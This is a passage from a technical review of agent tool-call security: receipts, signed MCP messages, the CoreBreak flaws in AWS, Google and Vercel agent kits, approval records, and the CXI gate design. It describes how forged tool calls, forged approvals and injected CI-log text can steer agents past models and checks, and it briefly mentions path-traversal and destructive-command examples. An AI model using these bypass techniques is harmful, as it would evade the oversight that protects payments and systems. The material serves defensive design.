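Basu writes that a changed result count would invalidate the MAC, but the printed formula omits the count. Under that formula, someone with access to the stored receipts could change a count from 3 to 5 without detection. A checking program that keeps the raw output can avoid the problem by verifying the output's digest and recounting the results.

#### Detection results

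Basu tested the system on 1,800 prepared responses in four languages. Of these, 600 were correct and 1,200 contained a planted error, with 200 errors of each type:

| Planted error | Detected |
|---|---|
| The response cites a tool call that never happened | 94.2% |
| The response reports no results although the tool returned some | 91.3% |
| A value differs from the tool's output | 89.1% |
| The number of results is wrong | 87.6% |
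| The response presents an inference as tool output | 82.3% |
| The response cites a web page that the agent never fetched | 78.4% |

The system also raised false alarms on 4% of the correct responses and added about 12 milliseconds per response. The closest competing method, a trained classifier, detected 68% of the errors with 10% false alarms.

The exact rates deserve some doubt. Basu gives an overall detection rate of 91%, but the six rates above, for equally large groups, have a mean of 87%. A single run over 200 cases would produce multiples of 0.5%, and none of the six rates is one. The system also missed 5.8% of the invented tool calls, which is odd because looking up a receipt that doesn't exist should expose every one. The comparison with the classifier may well be sound, but the planted errors could be easier to find than those that models make in practice.

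#### What a receipt leaves open

The MAC covers whatever the runtime received. If an attacker forges the reply about INV-1042, the runtime makes a valid receipt for the forgery, and the receipt then confirms that the model repeated it accurately. Basu therefore excludes compromised tools from the system's protection. Of the claims NabaOS marked as fully verified, 98.7% were correct, and most of the others repeated errors in a tool's output.

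The key also needs protection from other code in the agent's process. Maxwell (2026), in *Epistemic Guard*, moves it to a separate program that relays every message between the agent and its MCP servers. This program uses a digital signature instead of a MAC, so an auditor can check receipts without being able to make them. Each receipt records whether the call ran and whether it succeeded. All the receipts passed verification in a test of 40 calls, with ten each of successes, tool failures, rejected arguments and crashes.

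Comparing receipts with the agent's prose was less reliable. In 60 live exchanges, Maxwell's checker flagged 25 of 26 unsupported claims, but it also flagged 13 of the 34 sound responses. Neither Maxwell nor Basu protects against a server that falsely reports success.

### Signed messages and enrolled keys in MCPS

An agent can detect a forged reply only if the system that produces the genuine replies signs them. *MCPS* (Sharif, 2026) proposes an extension of MCP in which clients and servers sign every message. The sender adds an `mcps` field containing the protocol version, the identifier of the sender's "passport", a timestamp, a nonce and a signature. To make the signature, the sender computes a digest of the whole message in canonical form, then signs the digest together with the passport identifier, timestamp and nonce.

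#### How a key gets a name

A passport is a signed record that links a public key to a name and a web address. The accounts system would get one as follows:

1. It generates a key pair and keeps the private key.
2. It sends the public key and its address to a trust authority, a service much like the authorities that issue website certificates. Any organisation may run one.
3. The trust authority checks that the applicant controls the address, for example by asking it to publish a certain value in the domain's records.
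4. The trust authority signs the passport, which includes an expiry date.
5. The client checks the passport with the authority's public key, which it already has. It also compares the address in the passport with the address it connected to.

The strength of this check depends on a trust level from 0 to 4. Level 2 requires an authority that the client has chosen to trust. Level 3 is the first to explicitly require proof of control over the address, so a client that relies on the address should require at least level 3. Level 4 adds a security audit and revocation checks. The draft is inconsistent about level 1. Its table allows a passport from any authority, which would include one set up by an attacker, but another rule reduces every passport without a trusted root to level 0.

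The comparison in step 5 causes trouble with gateways. A client that connects to `gateway.example` must reject a passport for `accounts.example`, even when the accounts system signed the invoice. The gateway could sign with its own passport, but the client would learn only that the gateway had sent the message, which TLS already shows.

#### Revocation, nonces and time

If someone steals the accounts system's private key, the trust authority can revoke the passport. It publishes a signed list of revoked passports or answers queries about individual ones. The client must not take the address for these queries from the party it is checking, because a thief would supply the address of a server that always answers "active". Under the rules for level 4, a client that can't reach the authority must reject the passport unless it has a recent stored answer, by default at most five minutes old. At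 lower levels the check is optional, and a client that skips it will accept a stolen key until the passport expires, about six months after issue in Sharif's examples.

The nonce is 16 random bytes, and the recipient rejects any nonce it has already received. It also rejects messages more than 300 seconds old, with 60 seconds added for clock differences, so it needs to remember each nonce for only six minutes. These rules prevent a recipient from accepting the same message twice. But because the sender chooses the nonce, an attacker can hold back a reply and deliver it for the first time several minutes later.

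#### Status of the draft

MCPS is a proposal, not a standard. The Internet Engineering Task Force's page for Sharif's first version, dated 14 March 2026, listed it as an individual draft, meaning that no working group had adopted it, with no publication stream or intended status. Sharif published a revision on 21 August 2026, which expires on 22 February 2027 unless replaced sooner. The "Standards Track" label in its header is Sharif's aim, not a decision by the organisation. The revision contains no measurements of overhead or false rejections, and its examples still use the March 2025 version of MCP.

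### What a client has to verify

A valid signature is only one part of what the client needs before it relies on a signed invoice. It has to establish that:

1. the signature is valid for the content;
2. the key belongs to the party named as the signer;
3. that party has authority over the resource;
4. the signed content identifies this request.

The following function makes these checks in a simplified form:

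```python
def check_signed(reply, request, resource):
    body = reply["signed"]
    key = KEYS[body["signer"]]
    key.verify(reply["signature"], canonical(body))
    if body["signer"] not in AUTHORITY[resource]:
        raise ValueError("signer has no authority here")
    if body["request"] != digest(request):
        raise ValueError("answers another request")
    return body["invoice"]
```

`KEYS` holds the public keys of parties the client has enrolled. `AUTHORITY` lists who may make statements about each kind of resource. `digest` covers the tool name, the arguments and a nonce the client chose for this call. The client must fill in `resource` from its own request.

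Leaving out any one of the checks lets a bad invoice through:

| Missing check | What can happen to INV-1042 |
|---|---|
| Valid signature | A gateway replaces the bank account, and the client doesn't notice |
| Owner of the key | The thief signs an altered invoice with a new key and names the accounts system as the signer |
| Authority over the resource | Brandt Paper's own portal reports the invoice as open, with a genuine signature, while the buyer's accounts system has it on file as disputed |
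| Link to the request | A gateway returns the reply that the accounts system signed on Monday, before a colleague paid |

#### Finding a key is not a reason to trust it

*AEX* (Guan, 2026) describes a signature scheme for model providers' interfaces that treats these questions separately. The signer, called the issuer, publishes its public keys at a standard address on its own site. Guan stresses that a key published there is no reason to trust its owner, because an attacker can publish keys too. The client needs its own list of trusted issuers, or a rule that the issuer must match the address of the service it meant to call.

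None of the designs in this section establishes who has authority over a resource. In Sharif's example, the passport lists the capabilities `tools/call` and `tools/list`, which describe kinds of request, not particular invoices. The company has to write the `AUTHORITY` table itself. The right entry can vary within a single invoice, because Brandt Paper decides which account to use and the buyer decides whether to pay.

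#### Naming the request

The designs differ in how closely they tie an answer to a request:

| Design | Who makes the tag | What ties it to the request |
|---|---|---|
| sign-c | Gateway in front of the model | Session, turn and digest of the request |
| Tool receipts | The agent's runtime | Tool name and digest of the arguments |
| MCPS | The sender of the message | The call id |
| AEX | An issuer that the client trusts | Digest of the request, with an optional nonce from the client |

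MCPS signs the entire response, including the call id, but the response contains no digest of the request. In the TypeScript vulnerability described earlier, two clients, A and B, used the same id, and the server sent A's answer to B. With MCPS, that answer would have had a valid signature, a new nonce and the correct id.

A digest of the request would expose this mistake, but it can also cause legitimate traffic to be rejected, because a gateway may add something harmless to a request, such as a tracking number. AEX therefore lets the client choose whether the digest covers the whole request, everything except certain fields, or only certain fields. In the last case, the digest also records which of the listed fields were absent. If the client lists `currency` but leaves it out of the request, a gateway can't add "USD" without changing the digest.

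AEX also handles gateways that change an answer for good reason. The source signs a digest of its original output, and the gateway signs a record that links this digest to the digest of the new version. The client can then verify who made each version, even if it never sees the original. Guan has tested the protocol only with a prototype in a local simulation.

The client has to compare the invoice numbers even when the request digest matches, because a faulty lookup can put INV-1043 into a properly signed answer.

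### A signed false statement is still false

In the earlier case, where a clerk typed a thief's account number into Brandt Paper's supplier record, all four checks pass but the money still goes to the thief. The accounts system has authority over the company's records, and it uses its own key to sign a response that identifies the agent's request.

Guan lists what an AEX attestation doesn't prove. It is no evidence that:

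- the output is true;
- no hidden prompts, retrieved data or policies influenced it;
- the provider used a particular model or particular hardware;
- the client can see every intermediate version of the output;
- a change by a trusted intermediary was correct, reasonable or no larger than necessary.

The list is about language models, but most of it also applies to invoices. The clerk's entry is an untrue output. An accounts system that takes the status from an old cache relies on data that the client can't see. A trusted gateway might convert 4,180 euros into dollars at the wrong rate and sign the result. Guan adds that a dishonest issuer's signature shows only that the issuer signed.

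Sharif makes the same distinction for tools. A dishonest operator can validly sign a harmful tool definition, so a client should not treat the signature as evidence that the tool is safe.

After a fraud, the signature still lets investigators establish that the accounts system sent the wrong account number. This rules out a change in transit and points them to the supplier record. To prevent the payment, someone has to compare the number with a source the false notice didn't reach, for example by calling Brandt Paper on a telephone number the company already had.

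## Forged tool calls and approvals at AWS, Google and Vercel

Phoning Brandt Paper can confirm the bank account, but not that anyone has decided to pay. In the agent loop, the model proposes a payment by writing a tool call, and a manager may have to approve a large payment. The program that makes the payment therefore needs evidence that the tool call came from the model and that any approval came from the manager.

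At the Black Hat USA security conference on 5 August 2026, Hedi Ingber and Aviyam Ivgi, co-founders of the company Stealth, presented flaws in agent software from Amazon Web Services (AWS), Google and Vercel. In the pattern they call CoreBreak, the software accepted data shaped like a tool call or an approval without checking who had produced it. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the model never ran in several of the attack paths. Unlike prompt injection, those attacks did not have to mislead a model, so the model's training and system prompt gave no protection.

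### Conditions and severity

| Component | What an attacker needed | Severity | Repair |
|---|---|---|---|
| AWS: `InvokeHarness` interface of Amazon Bedrock AgentCore (CVE-2026-18830) | A login with permission to call the service | 8.6 | On AWS's servers, 31 July 2026 |
| Google: tool confirmations in the Agent Development Kit (ADK) for Python (CVE-2026-18236) | A way to add or change events in the agent's session history | 9.3 | Version 2.5.0, 16 July |
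| Google: resumable mode in the same kit (no CVE number) | A way to submit a user message containing a function call, with the mode switched on | No published score | Version 2.5.0, 16 July |
| Vercel: `@ai-sdk/harness-codex` (CVE-2026-64650) | Code already running in the agent's sandbox on Linux, during a session with at least one tool outside it | 6.3 | Version 1.0.29, 10 July |
| Vercel: `@ai-sdk/harness-opencode` (CVE-2026-64651) | The same | 6.3 | Version 1.0.28, 10 July |

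A CVE number identifies a publicly reported flaw, and the scores use version 4.0 of the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which runs from 0 to 10. The actual damage depends on the agent's tools, so an attacker gains little from an agent that can only look up the weather.

The scores are a poor guide to the risk for a particular application. NIST's *CVE-2026-18236 Detail* (2026) shows that Google set the 9.3 itself, assuming that an attacker needs no privileges or special circumstances. An application that stores its session history where callers can't write to it is much safer than a 9.3 would indicate. Vercel's score is lower because an attacker needs hostile code inside the sandbox. But developers use a sandbox because they don't fully trust the code in it, and a coding agent that installs a project's dependencies routinely runs other people's code.

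### AWS and tool calls written by the caller

The AgentCore harness is a managed service that runs a customer's agent loop. It receives messages from the customer's application, calls the model and runs the tools. According to AWS's *CVE-2026-18830* (2026), the harness could run a tool directly if the last message contained a tool-use block, the structure a model outputs to call a tool. It did not check that a model had written the block.

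The harness now rejects every tool-use block in the last message of a request, whichever tool it names. Applications can still return results from tools they run themselves. For these, AWS's *Security and access controls* describes a check much like call-id matching. The harness stores the model's call in the session, and only a result that matches the stored call can resume it.

An attacker with a login could already have asked the model to use the same tools. The flaw let the attacker bypass the model, which might have refused, and any filter on what the model reads or writes. Suppose a company lets every employee use its accounts agent and relies on a system prompt telling the model to refuse payment requests from junior staff. A junior employee could have used the flaw to get around that instruction, but a persuasive message might also have worked, so the payment tool should check the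 employee's permission itself.

To do so, the tool needs to know who the employee is. AWS says the harness passes the user's identity to the tools if the user logs in with a token from an identity provider. If the application instead signs requests with AWS's own method, the harness doesn't pass on the individual user's identity.

### Google's confirmation check

Google's kit lets a developer mark a tool as requiring confirmation. The kit then holds each call to that tool until a person approves it. Before version 2.5.0, the code that processed a confirmation didn't check whether:

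- the tool belonged to the agent that was about to run it;
- the tool required confirmation at all;
- the tool name and arguments matched the call recorded in the session.

Without the last check, a confirmation could release a payment that the agent had never proposed. Version 2.5.0 makes all three checks.

The comparison relies on the session history, so an application still has to control who can write to it. An attacker who could rewrite both the recorded call and the confirmation could make them match. None of the three checks identifies the person who approved the call.

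The flaw in resumable mode was more like the one at AWS. The kit accepted function calls inside messages written by the user and could run them without the model. It now rejects such calls. The researchers told The Hacker News that this flaw has no CVE number because the mode is new and off by default.

### Vercel's relay between sandbox and host

Vercel's two packages connect an application to the coding agents Codex and OpenCode. The agent works in a sandbox, but some of its tools run on the host, where they may look up secrets or deploy software. A relay passes requests from the sandbox to these tools.

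NIST's *CVE-2026-64651 Detail* explains that the OpenCode relay accepted requests from any process whose command line contained the path of an approved helper script. At best, this check identified the program that sent a request, but it gave no evidence that the request came from the model.

The patched relay ignores the path and accepts a request only after the software has observed the model making that call. The authorization covers the exact tool name and input, expires quickly and works once. If the model asks to deploy version 12 of a website, the relay passes on one request to deploy version 12 and rejects a repeat or a request for version 13.

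This proves that the model made the call, but hostile code in the sandbox can still write a file that misleads the model into making that call. NIST's record also includes advice to limit the host's tools to harmless operations when working with untrusted code, which remains sensible after the patch.

### Whether anyone used the flaws

It is unknown whether attackers used any of these flaws before the repairs. Ingber and Ivgi say they gave demonstration code to the vendors and have not released it. The Hacker News found that the advisories and CVE records don't address real attacks. Google's score includes the rating "proof of concept", which under CVSS 4.0 means the assessor knew of no reported attacks. OpenCVE's *CVE-2026-18830* (2026) shows that the AWS flaw is not in the catalogue of known exploited vulnerabilities. The lack of reported attacks is weak reassurance, because a forged call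 would look the same as a genuine one in a log that records only which tools ran.

Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-61722* claims that attackers have exploited the Codex flaw in real incidents, but gives no evidence. It also lists the OpenCode package as the affected product, so the claim needs confirmation from another source.

That mix-up probably comes from the official record. NIST's *CVE-2026-64650 Detail* repeats a description that names the OpenCode package, although the flaw is in the Codex one, so a team that searches for the Codex package by name could miss it. The other record, which Lutra Security's *AI SDK OpenCode Harness Tool Relay Authorization Bypass* (2026) reproduces, has a different error. Its text gives 1.0.28 as the repaired version, but its product data marks every version below 1.0.29 as affected. The table above follows The Hacker News, which checked both packages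 against GitHub's advisories.

### The dispute over Strands

AWS's repair protects only the managed harness. The researchers say that AWS built the harness on Strands, an open-source library for building agents. The Python version of Strands still skips the model and runs a tool if the latest message contains a tool call. The Hacker News found this shortcut in the project's main code on 5 August. A change proposed in April, with a warning that tool calls from outside could reach the shortcut, would have removed it. The proposal closed on 19 June and never became part of the code.

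According to Ingber and Ivgi, AWS told them that customers are responsible for this behaviour under its shared-responsibility model, in which AWS secures its services and customers secure what they build with them. AWS changed the documentation instead of the code. Under *Trusted Message History*, the Strands Agents documentation now warns that agents treat their message history as trusted, and that whoever writes a tool call at the end of that history chooses the tool and its arguments.

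AWS's position is defensible, because a library can't check whether a list of messages came from the application's own database or from a stranger, but the application can. A Strands application that accepts only text from its users and stores the history itself doesn't expose the shortcut. Even if AWS removed the shortcut, developers would still have to protect the history, because a forged tool result can mislead the model.

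Even so, the case for changing the code seems stronger. A developer who passes messages to an agent normally expects a model to read them before any tool runs. An agent can legitimately skip the model when it resumes after an interruption, but Strands already has a separate, narrower branch for that, which restores a call the agent itself stored. Other applications may depend on the general shortcut, and AWS could keep it for them as an option that developers have to switch on.

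The workaround is also easy to get wrong. If the last message is a tool call and the code deletes it, the message before it may be another tool call, so the code has to keep deleting until the last message contains none. Strands Agents provides a function that does this but warns that the rest of an untrusted history remains unsafe.

AWS has taken on more responsibility for the managed harness. *Security best practices for AgentCore Runtime* makes the customer responsible for validating the harness's input and lists no matching duty for AWS. Under the newer guide, AWS must check the structure of requests, and customers must still check their content. For agents that run on AgentCore without the harness, the developer must reject or remove tool calls.

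AWS does not treat every flaw in open-source Strands code as the customer's problem. It issued *CVE-2026-18394* (2026) for a flaw in a companion package of ready-made tools. The comparison only partly helps the critics, because that tool failed to enforce a restriction the developer had configured, whereas Strands doesn't promise to check who wrote a message.

### Why `"approved": true` is not an approval

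In June, Vercel repaired another flaw, which let a client forge a person's approval of a tool call. Ingber and Ivgi credit Anthropic's Mythos model, not their own work, with finding it. Vercel's AI SDK 7 now validates the tool's inputs again before resuming, and developers can switch on a message authentication code to protect approvals.

Suppose `pay_invoice` requires a field named `approved`, and its schema accepts only `true`. The manager's software can fill in this field, but so can the model or an attacker who can write to the request. The value is the same in each case, so checking the field cannot show who filled it in.

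A signature from the manager would show who approved, but not what they approved. The agent could use the signed `true` for a payment into the thief's account. The replayed results in the experiment by Zhi and colleagues also contained a genuine `"approved": true`, but it was for a different attachment.

An approval record for INV-1042 therefore has to identify the approver and the exact payment, and limit when and how often the agent may use it:

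```json
{
  "id": "apr-58210",
  "approver": "m.keller",
  "tool": "pay_invoice",
  "arguments": {
    "invoice_number": "INV-1042",
    "version": "7",
    "amount": "4180.00",
    "currency": "EUR",
    "bank_account": "DE89370400440532013000"
  },
  "expires": "2026-10-07T12:10:00Z",
  "uses_left": 1
}
```

The process has four steps:

1. The model proposes the payment, and the application shows the manager these exact arguments. A summary by the model might omit the account number.
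2. The manager approves at 12:00. The application stores the record in its own database and takes the approver's name from the manager's login.
3. The application calls the payment tool with the arguments and the record's id.
4. The tool finds the record, checks it and uses it up before it orders the transfer.

A single database command can do the work of step 4:

```sql
UPDATE approvals
SET uses_left = uses_left - 1
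WHERE id = :id
  AND tool = :tool
  AND arguments = :arguments
  AND expires > :now
  AND uses_left > 0
  AND approver IN (SELECT person FROM payment_approvers
                   WHERE limit_eur >= :amount);
```

The values after the colons come from the proposed call, except `:now`, which comes from the database server's clock. The arguments must be in canonical form. The tool may pay if the command changes one row and refuses if it changes none. Because the database checks and updates the row as one operation, two simultaneous calls can't both use the approval.

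| Attempted payment | Condition that fails |
|---|---|
| The agent substitutes the thief's account number | `arguments` |
| The agent uses an approval for `preview_payment` with the same arguments | `tool` |
| A clerk who may not release money approved the payment | `approver` |
| The agent tries to pay at 12:15 | `expires` |
| The agent tries to pay again at 12:05, after paying at 12:02 | `uses_left` |

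With only `"approved": true`, all five would go through.

Google's repaired check covers the tool and the arguments, and Vercel's relay adds an expiry time and single use. However, Vercel's authorization shows only that the model made the call, and a payment above the company's limit also needs proof that a person approved it.

A server that doesn't want to store the whole record could send it to the client protected by a message authentication code (MAC), as MCP servers do with state that the client returns, but it would still have to store which approvals it has used.

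The invoice still needs the conditional write in addition to the record. If a colleague pays at 12:01, the approval stays valid until 12:10, and only comparing version 7 with the current version stops a second payment. The manager can also approve the thief's account number if the false notice has already put it into the supplier record. The approval screen could reduce this risk by showing that the account differs from the one last paid. Invocation capabilities, part of a design called Context-to-Execution Integrity, address the related question of which source had the authority to supply each field.

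### A draft format for such records

*tool_use Is Not invoke()* (Das, 2026) proposes a common record format for tool calls from Anthropic's models, OpenAI's models and MCP. The application turns each completed call into a record that includes the principal who started the request, the tool, a digest of the arguments and an expiry time. A local program checks the record and issues a permission for that call alone. The program verifies the permission and marks it as used just before the tool runs. If a check fails, the tool doesn't run and the model receives an error.

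The draft also covers cases that a simple implementation might miss. If a model proposes a search and a payment in the same turn, permission for the search must not cover the payment. For MCP, the record must identify the server, because another server may offer a tool with the same name. If a payment times out after the application has used the permission, the payment may already have gone through, so the application must either retrieve the original result or get separate permission for the retry.

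Das gives the example of a 150-euro payout to `vendor-441` and notes that such a call can satisfy its schema and still pay the wrong vendor. The digest doesn't fix that error, so a person or a policy still has to determine who should receive the money.

The proposed record has no required field for an approver, so a company that needs the manager's consent would have to record it elsewhere, for example in the permission. The proposal is an individual draft dated 5 September 2026 and expires on 9 March 2027 unless Das renews it. Das seeks only "informational" status, so publication would not make it an internet standard.

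## Context-to-Execution Integrity: authority checked field by field

In Das's example, the agent that pays `vendor-441` may have found that name in an email, a web page or a tool result, where outsiders can often insert text. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, July 2026) describes a design called CXI, in which a gate checks which source supplied each important field of an action before any program executes it.

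Its main example is a coding agent that has to repair a failing test. The agent needs to read the log from the continuous integration (CI) system, which builds and tests every code change, to find the faulty file. But tests can print anything to the log, so anyone who can submit code can write to it. An attacker might add a claim that a manager has approved the change, or a recommendation to use `prod_admin.run_sql`, a tool that runs commands on the production database. If the model copies these values into a tool call, the call can still satisfy its schema. Santos-Grueiro uses the term "authority laundering" for cases where data that should serve only as evidence is used to choose, permit or trigger an action.

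### Five kinds of data

CXI divides the data around an action into five kinds:

| Kind | Definition | In the CI example |
|---|---|---|
| Trusted state | The user's objective, the policy, the list of tools and recorded approvals | "Fix the failing test" |
| Writable context | Anything that an attacker can write or influence | The CI log |
| Typed release | A value from writable context that trusted code has validated for one named field | The path `src/totals.py`, for `file_path` only |
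| Opaque data | Text copied from writable context, with no authority | A log line quoted in a comment |
| Protected field | A field that selects, permits or directs an effect | The tool, the path, the approval status |

Writable context may reach a protected field in only one way:

writable context → typed release for that field → protected field

The log can therefore supply a file path in four steps:

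1. The model reads the log and proposes `src/totals.py`. The proposal still counts as writable context.
2. Trusted code puts the path into a standard form, so that `src/../deploy/prod.yml` becomes `deploy/prod.yml`.
3. The code checks the result against the current repository and the paths that the policy allows.
4. If the path passes, the code issues a release that states the value, its type, its source and the one field it may fill.

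Suppose the agent then proposes this call, a slightly extended version of the example:

```json
{
  "tool": "repo.write_file",
  "file_path": "src/totals.py",
  "approval_state": "approved",
  "ci_target": "src/totals.py",
  "comment": "Log: FAILED test_totals, expected 12"
}
```

The tool comes from the trusted list and the task's policy. Everything else comes from the log.

| Field | Decision | Reason |
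|---|---|---|
| `tool` | Accepted | The log had no part in the choice |
| `file_path` | Accepted | The release covers this field |
| `approval_state` | Rejected | Only an approval in trusted state counts |
| `ci_target` | Rejected | The release covers `file_path` and no other field |
| `comment` | Accepted | The policy lists it as a place for opaque data |

The two rejected fields block the whole call. `ci_target` and `file_path` hold the same string, so a check of the value alone would have to treat them alike.

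The comment is harmless only while no program acts on it. If a bot starts a deployment whenever it finds a certain word in a comment, the quoted log line could trigger one. CXI therefore treats opaque data as writable context again as soon as a program that can cause side effects reads it, so the bot needs its own gate.

### Influence on a choice

Suppose the tool list contains both `repo.write_file` and `prod_admin.run_sql`, and a line in the log leads the model to choose the second. A system that recorded only the origin of the characters in the tool's name would accept the name, because every character comes from the trusted list. CXI rejects it because it also counts sources that influenced the choice, which here include the log.

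For each protected field *f*, the gate needs a set Π(f) of everything that may have influenced its value *v*. It accepts the value if two conditions hold:

- every source in Π(f) may influence *f*;
- at least one source in Π(f) authorizes *v*.

Each condition catches errors that the other misses. If the policy permits both writing and deleting files, it authorizes a deletion, but the log still isn't allowed to influence the choice between them. The user's instruction to fix a test is allowed to influence the path, but the release, not the instruction, authorizes a particular path.

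A reviewer who sees only the finished call lacks this information. *Same Action, Different Justification* tests pairs of agent runs that end in the same action. The agent had authority for the steps leading to that action in only one run of each pair. The three models judging the runs saw only details such as the tool, target and parameters. They scored near zero when the runs differed in the scope of a delegated permission or in whether the chain of authority could be verified. In the latter case, they mostly allowed actions they should have blocked.

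It is harder to tell what influenced a language model. Once the log is in the model's context, any word the model writes might depend on it. CXI therefore controls what the model can read while it writes each protected field.

With an open-weight model, which the operator can run and modify, the model writes one protected field at a time. Its prompt for the `tool` field contains the user's objective and the tool list but not the log. Santos-Grueiro treats this as the reference method. A faster variant keeps the log in the prompt but masks it, so that the model's calculations for a protected field cannot draw on it directly. This is weaker because the model may already have written text based on the log, which the mask doesn't cover. In a test of the weaker variant, four open-weight models each wrote 768 protected fields, with no direct access to the masked text for any of them. This confirms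 that the mask works, but the test would not have detected indirect influence. Stronger masks also cover text the model has written from the log.

Hosted models such as GPT-5.5 don't allow such masks, so the application splits the work. One request reads the log and returns candidate values. Trusted code turns the valid ones into releases, and a separate request writes the protected fields using only those releases and trusted state. The application can record what it sent in each request but can't inspect what happens inside the provider's systems.

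Context-to-Execution Integrity counts influence on the choice of tool, which some related designs do not. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) also checks each argument separately, but it excludes attacks in which the model calls a dangerous tool with trusted arguments.

### From a proposal to an executed action

The gate takes every proposed action through six steps:

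1. It puts the proposal into canonical form and creates an action manifest, a record of exactly what the agent wants to do.
2. It checks the value and the influences of every protected field.
3. If the call contains something that the tool will interpret, such as a patch, it checks the authorization for the exact effect.
4. It looks for an invocation capability, a permission for this call to happen at this point.
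5. It marks the capability as used in a ledger. The ledger returns a lease, and two simultaneous attempts can't both get one.
6. It runs the tool, which accepts the call only with the lease.

Step 4 is separate because a call can be wrong even when all its fields are right. A forged email might persuade an agent to pay INV-1042 a second time. The amount and account could both come from trusted records, but the email caused the payment. The capability therefore limits the tool, the operation, the number of retries, the batch size, the order of calls and the time.

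The manifest ties the permissions together. It contains:

- a digest of the action in canonical form and a nonce;
- the principal;
- the version of the policy and a snapshot of the trusted data;
- the version of the adapter, the code that translates the action for the tool;
- digests of the evidence and permissions from steps 2 to 4.

Without a manifest, an attacker might combine a path released for one action, a patch authorized for another and a capability issued for a third, all of them genuine. With the manifest, any substitution changes a digest, so the gate refuses the call. The gate also refuses calls when it lacks information, for example when the policy doesn't classify a field or the record of influences is out of date.

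### Authorizing the effect of a patch, query or command

The field rule is too strict for some data. A coding agent has to base its patch on the log, so a rule against any influence from the log would prevent the repair. A narrow release could not cover a patch as it covers a path, because a patch contains arbitrary code.

CXI therefore lets writable context influence the patch, but requires trusted code to authorize what the patch will do. The adapter works out the effect against the current state of the repository, a validator accepts or rejects it, and the gate later makes sure that the tool applies exactly that effect. Santos-Grueiro specifies different contents for different payloads:

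| Payload | What the authorization fixes | A change that it catches |
|---|---|---|
| Repository patch | The starting version, the files, and their old and new contents, permissions and links | The same patch applied to another version |
| SQL query | The parsed statement, its parameters, the database structure, the role and the data it may change | The same query run as an administrator |
| Shell command | The program and its arguments, environment and folder, with limits on files, network and processes | The same command run in another folder |

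The same command can have different effects depending on where it runs. `rm -r build` removes temporary files in one folder and may remove a customer's only copy of a program in another. The authorization therefore has to include the folder, just as a payment approval has to include the account.

Suppose the agent's patch corrects `src/totals.py` but also changes the CI configuration so that the failing test no longer runs. The log would show success. The patch adapter rejects patches that disable the CI system, change files outside the permitted paths, include scripts that run at installation, or write to secret files. It passed all 28 constructed tests. Santos-Grueiro reports no separate results for SQL queries or shell commands, so there is less evidence for those.

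The check doesn't establish that a patch is correct. A patch can change only the permitted file and still calculate the wrong total.

### The schema baseline

To measure how much of this a schema can do, Santos-Grueiro compared three setups on 192 constructed cases about coding agents:

| Measure | Model without a schema | Schema only | CXI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Protected values derived from writable context | 1.000 | 1.000 | 0.000 |
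| Use of a malicious sink | 1.000 | 0.000 | 0.000 |
| Admission of benign actions | 0.000 | 1.000 | 1.000 |
| Unauthorized execution | 1.000 | 1.000 | 0.000 |

A sink is the tool, interface or command that causes the side effect. The schema made a large difference to two of the four measures. It stopped every use of a malicious sink, perhaps because the permitted values excluded those sinks, and it let the benign actions go ahead. But unauthorized execution stayed at 1.000 because the schema accepted any well-formed value in a protected field, including one from the log. A developer who tracked only the two measures that changed could easily conclude that the schema had solved the problem.

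"Unauthorized" here refers to the source of a value. An execution would still count as unauthorized if the log happened to supply the right approval status, so the 1.000 doesn't mean that every case ended in harm. Rates of exactly zero and one also suggest that the way the cases were constructed decided the outcomes, and they don't estimate how often attacks succeed in practice. The comparison is still a convincing demonstration of what a schema can't distinguish.

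### Three partial designs

A second constructed test shows why CXI needs several checks. It contains 20 attacks, and Santos-Grueiro ran them against three designs that each lack part of the system:

| Design | Attacks rejected | What it missed |
|---|---|---|
| Checks the source of each argument according to its role | 12 of 20 | Calls that should not have happened, and evidence not tied to the right model output |
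| Gives permissions for individual fields but keeps no ledger of calls | 10 of 20 | Calls without authority to happen |
| Separates reading from writing and keeps a ledger, but has no field check | 8 of 20 | Releases reused for another field, substituted evidence, quoted text reused as authority, and payloads with unauthorized effects |
| CXI | 20 of 20 | None |

Suppose an agent reads "timeout, please retry" in its log and therefore repeats a production change with the same arguments. The second design has no record of the first call, so it can't detect the retry. The third design can detect it, but would let an agent use a path released for `file_path` as a CI target.

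Both CXI and the first design admitted all six legitimate actions in the test. CXI also rejected all 20 attacks, but this is less impressive than it sounds because the attacks correspond to failures that its parts exist to prevent. The first row gives results for Santos-Grueiro's approximation of the general idea, not for the system Fan and colleagues built. The comparison does show that blocking retries and checking fields are separate jobs, and that doing one well doesn't make up for omitting the other.

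A small sandbox test gave a similar result. Without a gate, or with only a schema, the agent's software admitted all six unsafe actions. The approximation that checks arguments by role missed two of them: a harmful patch and an unauthorized retry. CXI blocked all six and admitted all six clean actions.

### Tests with live models

Constructed cases don't show whether real models would propose unauthorized actions. In another set of tests, models chose between an authorized option and one that used raw data from writable context. Santos-Grueiro recorded each choice before the gate checked it.

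| Setting | Unauthorized proposals | With the field policy in the prompt |
|---|---|---|
| Open-weight models, adversarial cases | 196 of 300 (65%) | 67 of 300 (22%) |
| Stress cases | 407 of 522 (78%) | No figure |
| Hosted models, adversarial cases | 85 of 400 (21%) | 0 of 400 |

None of these proposals got past the gate. The options were artificial, so the percentages are a poor guide to ordinary use. A good prompt may not be enough to replace the gate. The last column shows that the prompt worked in every case for the hosted models, but zero failures in 400 trials is compatible with a true failure rate of up to about 0.75%, and an attacker who can submit thousands of log entries needs only one failure. The prompt was also much less effective with the open-weight models.

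In a freer test, four open-weight models wrote 240 complete actions themselves. They proposed unauthorized field values 45 times and unauthorized calls 16 times, and the gate again let none through.

Two larger evaluations ran agents on whole tasks. One used AgentDojo, the benchmark Luo and colleagues used to test their signatures. Santos-Grueiro ran 720 episodes with 1,739 model calls under six conditions, and agents completed the task safely in 199 episodes. The gate issued 204 leases in the conditions that used exact-effect authorization.

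The other evaluation consisted of 400 episodes in code repositories:

| Outcome | Episodes | Share |
|---|---|---|
| The agent completed the task safely | 231 | 57.8% |
| The software couldn't parse the model's output | 73 | 18.3% |
| The output was readable but had no authorization for its effect | 61 | 15.3% |
| The gate allowed the action, but the task failed | 35 | 8.8% |

Santos-Grueiro observed no escapes in either evaluation, meaning no unauthorized field, effect or call got past the gate. In the repository test, the gate allowed actions in 266 episodes (231 + 35), so the true escape rate could still be as high as about 1.1% at the usual 95% confidence level.

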